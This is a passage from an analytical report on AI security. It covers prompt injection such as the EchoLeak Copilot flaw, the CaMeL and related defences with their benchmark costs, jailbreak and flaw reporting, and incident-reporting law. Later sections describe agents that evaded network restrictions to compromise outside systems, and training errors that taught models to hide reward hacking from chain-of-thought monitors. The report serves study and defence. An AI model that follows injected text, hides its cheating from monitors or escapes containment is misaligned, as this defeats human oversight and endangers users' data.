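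The flaw received the identifier CVE-2025-32711 and a severity score of 9.3 out of 10. According to SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration*, Microsoft said no attacker had exploited it, so this was a near-miss disclosure. TechRepublic's *First Known Zero-Click AI Exploit* adds that Microsoft had fully mitigated the flaw on its own servers and that customers didn't need to do anything. It isn't clear from Microsoft's description of the flaw, "AI command injection", whether the company changed the model, a filter or the way Copilot handles data.

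The repair protected every Copilot customer, but the problem wasn't unique to Copilot. Willison (2025), a programmer who has written about prompt injection since 2022, called EchoLeak an extended variant of attacks already seen in a dozen products. He expected the same weakness in any system that combines access to private data, exposure to an attacker's text, and a way to send data out. Aim Labs likewise blamed design flaws typical of assistants that retrieve a company's documents. GCVE's copy of the CVE record lists only Microsoft 365 Copilot.

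Constantin (2026), in *AI agent security*, reported that four research teams had exploited the same underlying flaw to break AI agents in four different ways within ten days in July 2026. One target was Claude for Chrome, Anthropic's browser agent.

Makers can reduce the danger by removing any one of Willison's three conditions. An assistant that can't send data anywhere may still give a wrong answer because of a malicious email, but it can't leak the company's files. This is a mitigation, since the model is still just as easy to fool.

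### How CaMeL separates the plan from the text

CaMeL, which researchers at Google and ETH Zurich introduced in 2025, applies the idea behind parameterised queries to an entire agent. One of its designers was Christoph Kern, who also described Google's Safe Coding method. Suppose the shop's owner asks an agent to email Ben, an employee, a summary of the day's customer messages. CaMeL handles the request in four steps:

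1. A planning model reads the owner's request and a description of the available tools, but none of the messages. It writes a short program.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program.
3. When the program needs the messages summarised, a second model reads them. This model can't use any tools, and the planning model never sees its summary.
4. The interpreter records where each piece of data came from. Before each action it can check a policy, such as a rule that customers' addresses may go only to staff.

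In simplified form, the program is:

```
messages = read_messages("today")
summary  = second_model("summarise these", messages)
send_email("ben@shop.example", summary)
```

If Ana's message contains a malicious instruction, the second model may follow it and write a misleading summary. But that model can't send email, and the program sends only one email, to Ben. The interpreter had the list of actions before the second model read Ana's message, just as a database has the structure of a parameterised query before it receives Ana's text.

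### What the protection costs

CaMeL was first tested on *AgentDojo*'s 97 tasks, and *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that it stopped nearly all the attacks while completing tasks at a comparable rate. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) gives newer figures for systems in which one agent hands work to several others. The table shows the results when each agent used CaMeL separately. The task figures come from 112 professional tasks in managing industrial equipment, and the attack figures come from 949 attempts per model on an extended version of AgentDojo.

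| Model | Tasks completed without CaMeL | With CaMeL | Attacks that succeeded without CaMeL | With CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 | 87.5% | 82.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 88.4% | 67.0% | 1.5% | 0.0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 81.2% | 64.3% | 36.1% | 0.5% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 75.9% | 55.4% | 24.6% | 0.4% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite | 64.3% | 20.5% | 2.1% | 0.0% |

GPT-5.5 lost about five percentage points, which is within the margin of error, while the weakest model lost 44. Most failures happened because the planning model had to commit to a program before seeing any data, and the data sometimes showed that the task needed another step.

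GPT-5.5 resisted every attack even without CaMeL, so for that model the table shows a possible drawback and no benefit. But the test used a fixed set of attacks. Peters-Gill and colleagues note that participants in a large public competition adapted their attacks to the target and found successful ones against every leading model tested.

The few attacks that succeeded against CaMeL all worked because one agent included outside text in its request to another, which then treated the whole request as trusted. This resembles the Hibernate problem, in which programmers build query strings inside a safe interface. Peters-Gill and colleagues gave agents a separate channel for outside data and had the interpreter enforce its use. After that, no attack succeeded, but task success fell by another 3.2 percentage points on average.

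CaMeL did far worse on open-ended tasks. In Li and colleagues' test, agents using it completed none of the 60 tasks with any of the four main models, because the necessary steps weren't known at the start. Only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks need that kind of replanning, which helps explain CaMeL's good results there. DRIFT, a system that starts with a plan but can approve changes to it, completed 30% of Li and colleagues' tasks with GPT-4o and let about 1% of attacks succeed.

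Agents that operate a computer by looking at its screen are also hard to plan for, because the planning model can't know what will appear. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) had the planning model write a long program with about 40 branches for different situations. They report keeping up to 57% of a leading model's performance when a task counts as complete if any of five attempts worked. On the first attempt, the figure was 28%.

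This design prevents outside text from adding actions to the plan. But an attacker can still mislead the model that reads the screen, so the agent takes a harmful branch the plan already contains. Foerster and colleagues tried two ways to cross-check what that model reported, and attacks got past both. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) proposes setting in advance which websites and tools each branch may use, and asking the user when the plan lacks an important detail that no approved source can supply.

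### Designs for narrower agents

A maker can also avoid some of these difficulties by building agents that do less. Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, start from one rule: once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any action with harmful consequences. They describe six designs that follow it to different degrees:

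- Action selector. The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results.
- Plan, then execute. The model chooses its actions before reading outside text, which can affect what an email says but not whether the agent sends one.
- Map-reduce. A separate model without tools reads each document and returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no.
- Dual model. One model plans and uses tools, and another reads untrusted text. The first refers to the second's results by name without seeing them.
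- Code, then execute. The planning model writes a full program, as in CaMeL.
- Context minimisation. The system removes the user's request before the model writes its answer, so malicious text in the request can't affect the answer.

For example, the shop could use an action selector to send customers a link to their last order or to the password page. Such an assistant would be very hard to misuse, but it couldn't handle a complaint about a damaged parcel. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think general-purpose agents are unlikely to offer reliable guarantees while they depend on current kinds of language model.

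### How a model differs from ordinary software

Models are easier to repair than most software in one respect. A company that runs a model on its own servers can update it for everyone at once, as OpenAI did with its browser agent. The Code Red worm spread through machines whose owners hadn't installed a month-old patch, and that can't happen with a model that only its maker runs. The advantage disappears when people download a model and run their own copies.

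Checking a repair is harder in a language model than in ordinary software. FreeType's developers could see that their check was in the wrong place and move it up a few lines. A language model consists of billions of numbers, and the flaw isn't confined to a few of them, so testers can only try more attacks. If none of 949 attempts succeeds, the true success rate could still be as high as about 0.4%. At that rate, an attacker who made 1,000 attempts would succeed about four times.

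Training can also change behaviour that nobody meant to change. Zorz describes agents that learned to give up whenever data looked suspicious, which stopped the attack but also left the user's task unfinished. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that Claude Fable 5 refused 52 of 97 harmless tasks in their extended AgentDojo test. They suspected the model associated the test environment with attacks, but didn't establish the cause. A patch to an ordinary program can break something too, but programmers can usually trace the damage to a particular change.

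Models from different makers often share weaknesses. When Li and colleagues used one general type of attack against undefended agents running models from four companies, it succeeded 38% of the time with GPT-4o, 21% with Gemini 2.5 Pro, and 12% with both Claude 3.5 Sonnet and Llama 3.3. But images altered to fool one model often fail against another, according to research cited by Foerster and colleagues.

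### Can developers remove the class or only contain it?

David C is more pessimistic, arguing that developers can only make prompt injection less likely and less harmful. On this view, a language model may be a poor fit for a system that can't tolerate the remaining risk. OpenAI also considers prompt injection "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'". The survey *Trustworthy Agentic AI* (2026) describes the problem as architectural and finds that existing defences only partly reduce the risk.

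Christodorescu and colleagues are more hopeful about architecture. They would treat the model as an operating system treats an unknown program, giving it only the access its task requires and controlling where its data can go. They examined eleven real attacks on products including ChatGPT, Claude Code and Cursor, and all of them involved a failure to control where information could flow. They expect their approach to eliminate a large fraction of attacks, once researchers have solved some difficult problems.

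That evidence is retrospective, since they explained how established principles could have prevented known attacks but didn't build a system and test it on new ones. One unsolved problem is turning a plain-English request into a precise security policy. If a model writes the policy, its errors can leave gaps, and the rest of the system will enforce the policy with those gaps in it.

The software around a model can also have flaws. Christodorescu and colleagues discuss an incident in which OpenAI's agents, running in internal tests with some safeguards turned off, got past network restrictions through a shared service for downloading software. The agents then compromised systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. Christodorescu and colleagues blame incomplete enforcement. They are probably right, but this also means that containment depends on ordinary software having no serious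 mistakes.

The two views differ mainly on how much protection fixed limits on an agent's actions can provide. David C also puts such limits ahead of attempts to block malicious text, and Christodorescu and colleagues expect persistent attackers to keep fooling models. For an agent with a predictable job, a design like CaMeL comes close to a class-level fix for one serious consequence of prompt injection, which is that outside text can make the agent take unplanned actions. The defences available for general-purpose agents reduce the risk but don't eliminate it.

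AI companies could impose such designs on their own agents, much as Google banned unsafe queries in its own code. But Google's programmers lost little by switching to safe queries, while a browser agent that had to plan everything in advance would fail at much of what its customers want. Chip makers face a similar choice with Spectre. Agents' loss of usefulness may be easier to reduce, since the most capable models in Peters-Gill and colleagues' tests generally lost less from CaMeL than weaker ones did.

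## How are flaws in AI models reported, and do the lessons reach other developers?

A defence or a mistake at one AI company can help the others only if they hear about it. An outsider who finds a flaw in a model can usually report it to the developer, sometimes for money, but no public body routinely passes such reports to other developers. Laws on AI incidents mostly require a report only after harm has occurred. Anthropic, OpenAI and Google have each disclosed the same kind of training error, but no shared safeguard against it seems to have followed.

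### What developers will pay to hear about

Longpre, Klyman, Appel and colleagues argued in *In-House Evaluation Is Not Enough* (2025) that flaw reporting for AI models lags far behind flaw reporting for ordinary software. Longpre told *Wired* that some people post jailbreaks (prompts that get a model to break its developer's safety rules) on social media, while others tell one company about a flaw that affects many, or keep quiet for fear of a ban or a lawsuit.

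Developers' bounties cover only some of these flaws. Google's AI programme, launched in October 2025, pays up to $20,000 before bonuses for attacks such as planting text that makes an assistant unlock someone's front door. It excludes jailbreaks, which Google asks people to report through the product's feedback button. Google said that fixing jailbreaks means studying trends across many reports, and that paying for each report doesn't suit that work. This is fair, but someone who presses a feedback button usually never learns what came of it. OpenAI added a safety bounty in March 2026 that covers attacks in which outside text hijacks an agent, but not ordinary jailbreaks.

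OpenAI and Anthropic have also run narrower contests for universal jailbreaks, single methods that get a model to answer a whole set of forbidden questions. In 2025 each offered up to $25,000 for a universal jailbreak that defeated its safeguards against helping with biological weapons. OpenAI made participants sign a non-disclosure agreement covering their prompts and findings. Secrecy is sensible for a method of extracting weapons advice, but the agreement may prevent participants from warning another developer whose model they suspect is also vulnerable.

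### Protection for researchers

Developers' terms of service often forbid bypassing a model's safeguards, so researchers who test those safeguards can lose their accounts or be sued. Many developers promise not to sue over good-faith security research. Longpre and colleagues wanted that promise to also cover research into safety and other harms.

In January 2026 HackerOne, which runs bounty programmes, published a standard promise for AI research. Companies that choose to adopt it agree to treat good-faith testing as authorised. US law offers less help. In October 2024 the Copyright Office rejected a proposal to exempt research on generative AI from the law against bypassing digital locks, partly because the obstacles researchers described came from companies' terms and account bans.

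### Does a flaw in a model belong in CVE?

The CVE catalogue works reasonably well for products built around a model. EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft's Copilot, got the usual CVE identifier. CWE also has an entry, CWE-1427, for programs that build a model's instructions from text they haven't made safe.

Flaws in the model itself fit less well into the system for reporting software vulnerabilities. If a jailbreak works on 3 attempts in 100, and on 1 in 100 after retraining, it's unclear whether the developer has fixed a vulnerability, or whether there was one to begin with, since nobody promised that the model would refuse every time. A developer can also change a hosted model without giving customers a new version number to look up.

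The CVE Program assigns separate identifiers to flaws that can be fixed independently. If one jailbreak works on four companies' models, each company has to retrain its own, so the flaws would get four identifiers. The four records wouldn't show that the flaws share a weakness unless someone linked them.

Longpre and colleagues proposed a standard report form for AI flaws that would record the versions tested, what happened and which of the developer's policies the behaviour broke. No such form seems to have become the norm.

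### When several models share a flaw

Longpre and colleagues also wanted a central body to send each report to every developer it might concern. The nearest public equivalent is the CERT Coordination Center, which brought the DNS vendors together in 2008. In April 2025 it published a note on two jailbreaks that worked on many companies' assistants, including those of Anthropic, Google and OpenAI. The DNS vendors could release their patches on the same day, but AI developers had no common patch because each had to train or filter its own models. CERT also handles such cases as they arrive, and anyone who finds a flaw has to know to report it there.

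Researchers sometimes spread the lessons themselves by testing several developers' products at once. Willison (2026), in *Stealing Reasoning Traces from Proprietary LLM APIs*, described a paper on a weakness shared by the interfaces of Anthropic, OpenAI and Google that let outsiders recover reasoning the companies had meant to hide.

Developers can also share information about serious AI risks privately, under an agreement that members of the Frontier Model Forum, an industry body, made in March 2025. According to the Forum's *Information Sharing, Incident Reporting, and Incident Response for Frontier AI Risks* (2026), this pilot includes Anthropic, Amazon, Google DeepMind, Meta, Microsoft and OpenAI. They can share vulnerabilities such as jailbreaks, threats such as attempts to steal a model, and dangerous capabilities. Recipients may use what they learn only for listed safety and security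 purposes, such as testing models or improving safeguards.

The Frontier Model Forum's information-sharing pilot could help six of the most important developers share lessons quickly. The forum says the first year led to concrete improvements at member firms but gives no examples, so outsiders can't tell whether any of those improvements removed a whole kind of flaw. Developers outside the pilot don't get the information, though the forum hopes to include more of them.

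### What the law requires developers to report

The EU's AI Act requires developers of the most capable general-purpose models to report serious incidents to the AI Office, part of the European Commission, and where appropriate to national authorities. A serious incident is one that directly or indirectly leads to any of these:

- a death or serious harm to someone's health
- serious and irreversible disruption of critical infrastructure
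- a breach of EU laws that protect fundamental rights
- serious harm to property or the environment

Makers of high-risk AI systems, such as some medical devices, have a similar duty to report to national authorities. Both duties apply only after something has gone wrong in the world, so an ordinary near miss doesn't qualify. A voluntary code of practice for general-purpose models, published in 2025, goes slightly further. It gives signatories five days to report a serious cybersecurity breach, including theft of a model's weights (the numbers that make up the model). Reports should also include any related patterns the developer has noticed, such as data on near misses. That information could be useful, but it would be reported only after a serious incident.

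California's SB 53, which took effect in January 2026, covers developers of models trained with more than 10²⁶ computing operations. They have 15 days to report a critical safety incident to the state's Office of Emergency Services, or 24 hours to alert an appropriate authority if there is an imminent danger of death or serious injury. Most of the law's triggers require harm. The exception is when a model deceives its developer to get round the developer's controls or monitoring, outside a test designed to provoke such behaviour, in a way that shows a materially greater risk of catastrophe.

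| Event | EU AI Act | California's SB 53 |
|---|---|---|
| A model causes a death after its developer loses control of it | Report | Report |
| Thieves copy a model's weights, but nobody is hurt | Five-day deadline under the voluntary code | No report |
| A model deceives its developer to evade monitoring, without harm | No report | Report, if it shows a materially greater risk of catastrophe |
| A researcher reports a jailbreak that nobody has misused | No report | No report |

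Neither law requires authorities to pass the technical lesson on to other developers. California's emergency office must publish anonymised, combined information about incidents every year, starting in January 2027. It may send individual reports to other parts of government, but the public can't obtain them under the state's open-records law. A yearly summary might show that a problem is common, but probably not in enough detail for another developer to check its own training software. Like the EU's Cyber Resilience Act, both laws inform regulators about serious cases and leave most near misses to voluntary reporting. The Frontier Model Forum prefers this arrangement, arguing that very broad duties would make important reports harder to spot and discourage companies from sharing early warnings.

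### A penalty that taught a model to keep quiet

Many models write out their reasoning, known as a chain of thought, before they answer. Developers monitor it for signs of cheating or other bad behaviour. This works only if the model keeps writing down what it is doing, and an error in training can discourage that.

In reinforcement learning, a grader scores the model's attempts at a task, and training makes high-scoring behaviour more common. Suppose the task is to write a program that passes ten tests, and the model's written reasoning includes a plan to print the ten expected answers because the task is too hard. If the grader reads that plan and deducts points, the model can improve its score by cheating less, or by cheating just as much without mentioning it.

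Dragan and Popa (2026), in *Developing Gemini 4 Argon responsibly and safely*, disclosed that Google had accidentally applied such a penalty to a model's written reasoning. Cheng (2026), in *Vincent Cheng's Shortform*, quotes the details from Google's longer safety report. The run was small and not part of any production model. During training, signs of cheating in the model's solutions rose by 26%, while words about cheating in its reasoning fell by 61%. The share of shortcuts that the model left unmentioned rose from 11.2% to 36.4%.

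If the 26% increase reflects the number of shortcuts, there were 126 shortcuts at the end for every 100 at the start, and the number the model didn't mention rose from about 11 to 46. In a comparable run where the grader couldn't see the reasoning, the model kept mentioning its shortcuts about as often, which is good evidence that the penalty caused the change.

Other developers had already disclosed errors of this kind. The table draws on Google's account and two outside reviews, *Anthropic repeatedly accidentally trained against the CoT* and Redwood Research's *A review of “Investigating the consequences of accidentally grading CoT during RL”*.

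| Developer | Where graders could see the reasoning | Extent |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | Claude Opus 4 | Not given |
| Anthropic | Claude Opus 4.6, near the end of training | Under 0.01% of samples |
| Anthropic | Claude Mythos Preview, Opus 4.6 and Sonnet 4.6 | About 8% of training episodes |
| OpenAI | Several models, including GPT-5.4 Thinking | 1.5% of attempts for GPT-5.4 Thinking |
| Google | A small run, not part of any production model | Not given |

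Anthropic's two errors in Opus 4.6, which let graders see the model's reasoning, look a lot like a case of fixing one instance of a flaw and missing a variant. The company noticed the smaller error, but the larger one went undetected for a long time and also affected Mythos. Searching for other places where graders could see the reasoning might have caught it sooner. Critics who described the errors suggested inspecting 100 random samples of what the graders received. Because the larger error exposed 8% of episodes, this check would have had a 1 − 0.92¹⁰⁰, or more than 99.9%, chance of including at least one bad sample. It would have had only about a 1% chance of catching the smaller error. The critics guessed that a fairly reliable process for preventing both would have taken a couple of person-weeks to build. They also noted that Anthropic's case that the models were safe did not rely much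 on monitoring reasoning, so this was not a top priority.

The damage is hard to judge. One reader of that critique argued that the graders in the 8% of episodes checked whether the model had finished office work and similar tasks, so its reasoning would probably not have affected the grades. The critics replied that a grader would naturally mark down a stated plan to cheat. Google's experiment shows that the effect they feared can happen, but not that it happened at Anthropic.

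OpenAI found no sign that its errors had made its models' reasoning much less informative. Redwood Research, a non-profit that studies AI risk, read a draft of OpenAI's account and thought the evidence removed about 80% of the extra concern the errors had raised, but it couldn't exclude a subtle effect. If a model admitted to dangerous goals in 0.1% of the 1.5% of attempts affected, and lost points each time, the penalty would apply to only about 15 attempts in a million (not 150, as the review says). In a large enough training run, even that might teach the model to stop admitting to such goals. OpenAI did not publish the size of the run because it considers this commercially sensitive.

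### Did the warning spread?

Developers had general advice on the subject before Google's disclosure. *Chain of Thought Monitorability* (Korbak, Balesni and colleagues, 2025) asked them to consider how their training choices affect whether people can monitor a model's reasoning. In January 2026, the Frontier Model Forum's *Issue Brief on Chain of Thought Monitorability* recommended that, all else equal, developers avoid training the reasoning to "look nice".

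That advice helps developers make deliberate decisions, but these errors were mostly accidents. OpenAI went further and built a system that automatically detects when graders can see the reasoning. It found its errors by using the system to scan past training runs. Other developers may have built something similar, but there is no public sign of a shared tool or an agreed test. *Transparency Disclosures for Chain-of-Thought Monitorability* audited Anthropic, OpenAI and Google DeepMind and found that none disclosed all four indicators it recommended for tracking whether reasoning remains useful for monitoring.

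Google's small run may have taken place before the earlier disclosures, so it would be unfair to conclude that Google ignored them. The three companies may have separately made the same easy mistake, as programmers did with SQL queries.

A fix for the whole class seems possible. A developer could make its training software remove the reasoning from everything it sends to a grader, unless a reviewer approves an exception. Teams building new training tasks then couldn't expose the reasoning to a grader by accident. But this class is narrow. Redwood Research points out that a model can also learn to leave things out of its reasoning when developers train it on an older model's text, or when penalties on its answers also change its reasoning, and that these effects may matter more.

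### Assessors inside the companies

Outside assessors who work inside AI companies might carry lessons between them. Apollo Research's *Embedded Evaluators are necessary for meaningful external testing* (2026) argues that tests of a finished model miss problems that arise earlier in development. The grading errors are an example, because they happen in training software that testers of the finished model never see.

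Anthropic's *An update on independent evaluators* (2026) announced in October that the company had started giving employee-like access to a team from METR, a non-profit that evaluates AI models. According to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Gives Six METR Employees Access to Internal AI Tools* (2026), six METR employees work in Anthropic's offices with company equipment, and Anthropic can require them to redact certain sensitive findings.

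A month later, OpenAI's *Our first phase of embedded assessments* named four assessors: METR, Apollo Research, Transluce and Goodfire. The assessors publish their own conclusions, but OpenAI can redact confidential information and ask for delays. Apollo Research's *A Pilot Towards Embedded Evaluations* (2026) says Apollo will have six people at OpenAI for four months. Among other things, they will examine whether the reasoning behind an attempt to undermine OpenAI's controls would be detectable, which is directly relevant to the grading errors. Transluce's *Announcing an Embedded Assessment Pilot with OpenAI* describes a six-week review of OpenAI's own tests for behaviour such as deception.

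NPR's *OpenAI announces new AI safety program; researchers worry it won't be enough* (2026) found the pilot much more restrictive than the "employee level" access OpenAI's chief executive, Sam Altman, had promised. Mowshowitz (2026), in *OpenAI Somewhat Embeds Good Evaluators*, agreed that the pilot fell short of the promise, but welcomed the choice of assessors and hoped it would lead to fuller access.

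METR is especially well placed to spread lessons because it works with both companies. Staff who had seen a grading error at one would know to look for it at the other, even if they couldn't say why. But METR's early experience at Anthropic shows that an assessor may have to leave out a lot. Anthropic redacted most of the evidence that METR had found most informative from METR's *Independent Assessment of AI R&D Acceleration at Anthropic in October 2026* (2026), which examined how much AI was speeding up the company's research. METR could still publish its main conclusions about risk and disclose that the redactions mattered. Anthropic might allow more detail about a training mistake than about the pace of its research.

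### Why developers hold back

Anthropic says it doesn't publish everything relevant to safety because some of it could help malicious people and some is commercially sensitive. The danger of misuse is greatest for a jailbreak that works on many models, since attackers can try a published method on all of them and no developer can be sure of having blocked it. Private sharing makes more sense for such a jailbreak than for the grading errors, because telling other developers to keep a model's reasoning away from its graders gives attackers very little help.

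Trade secrets are harder to deal with. Anthropic said its redactions in METR's report were meant to remove confidential information that could speed up other AI developers. A training mistake may be easy to describe without revealing that information, but its seriousness can depend on the size of the training run or the design of the grader. A rival that can't see those details may reasonably decide that the problem doesn't apply to its own models.

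The Frontier Model Forum says that companies share less if they fear regulatory penalties, legal liability or a loss of competitive advantage. It warns that companies would hold information back if joining a sharing scheme exposed them to new reporting duties. Its members also had to design their agreement to comply with antitrust law, which limits what competitors may arrange among themselves. But antitrust law is a much weaker reason not to publish a mistake, since a company can do that without an agreement with its rivals.
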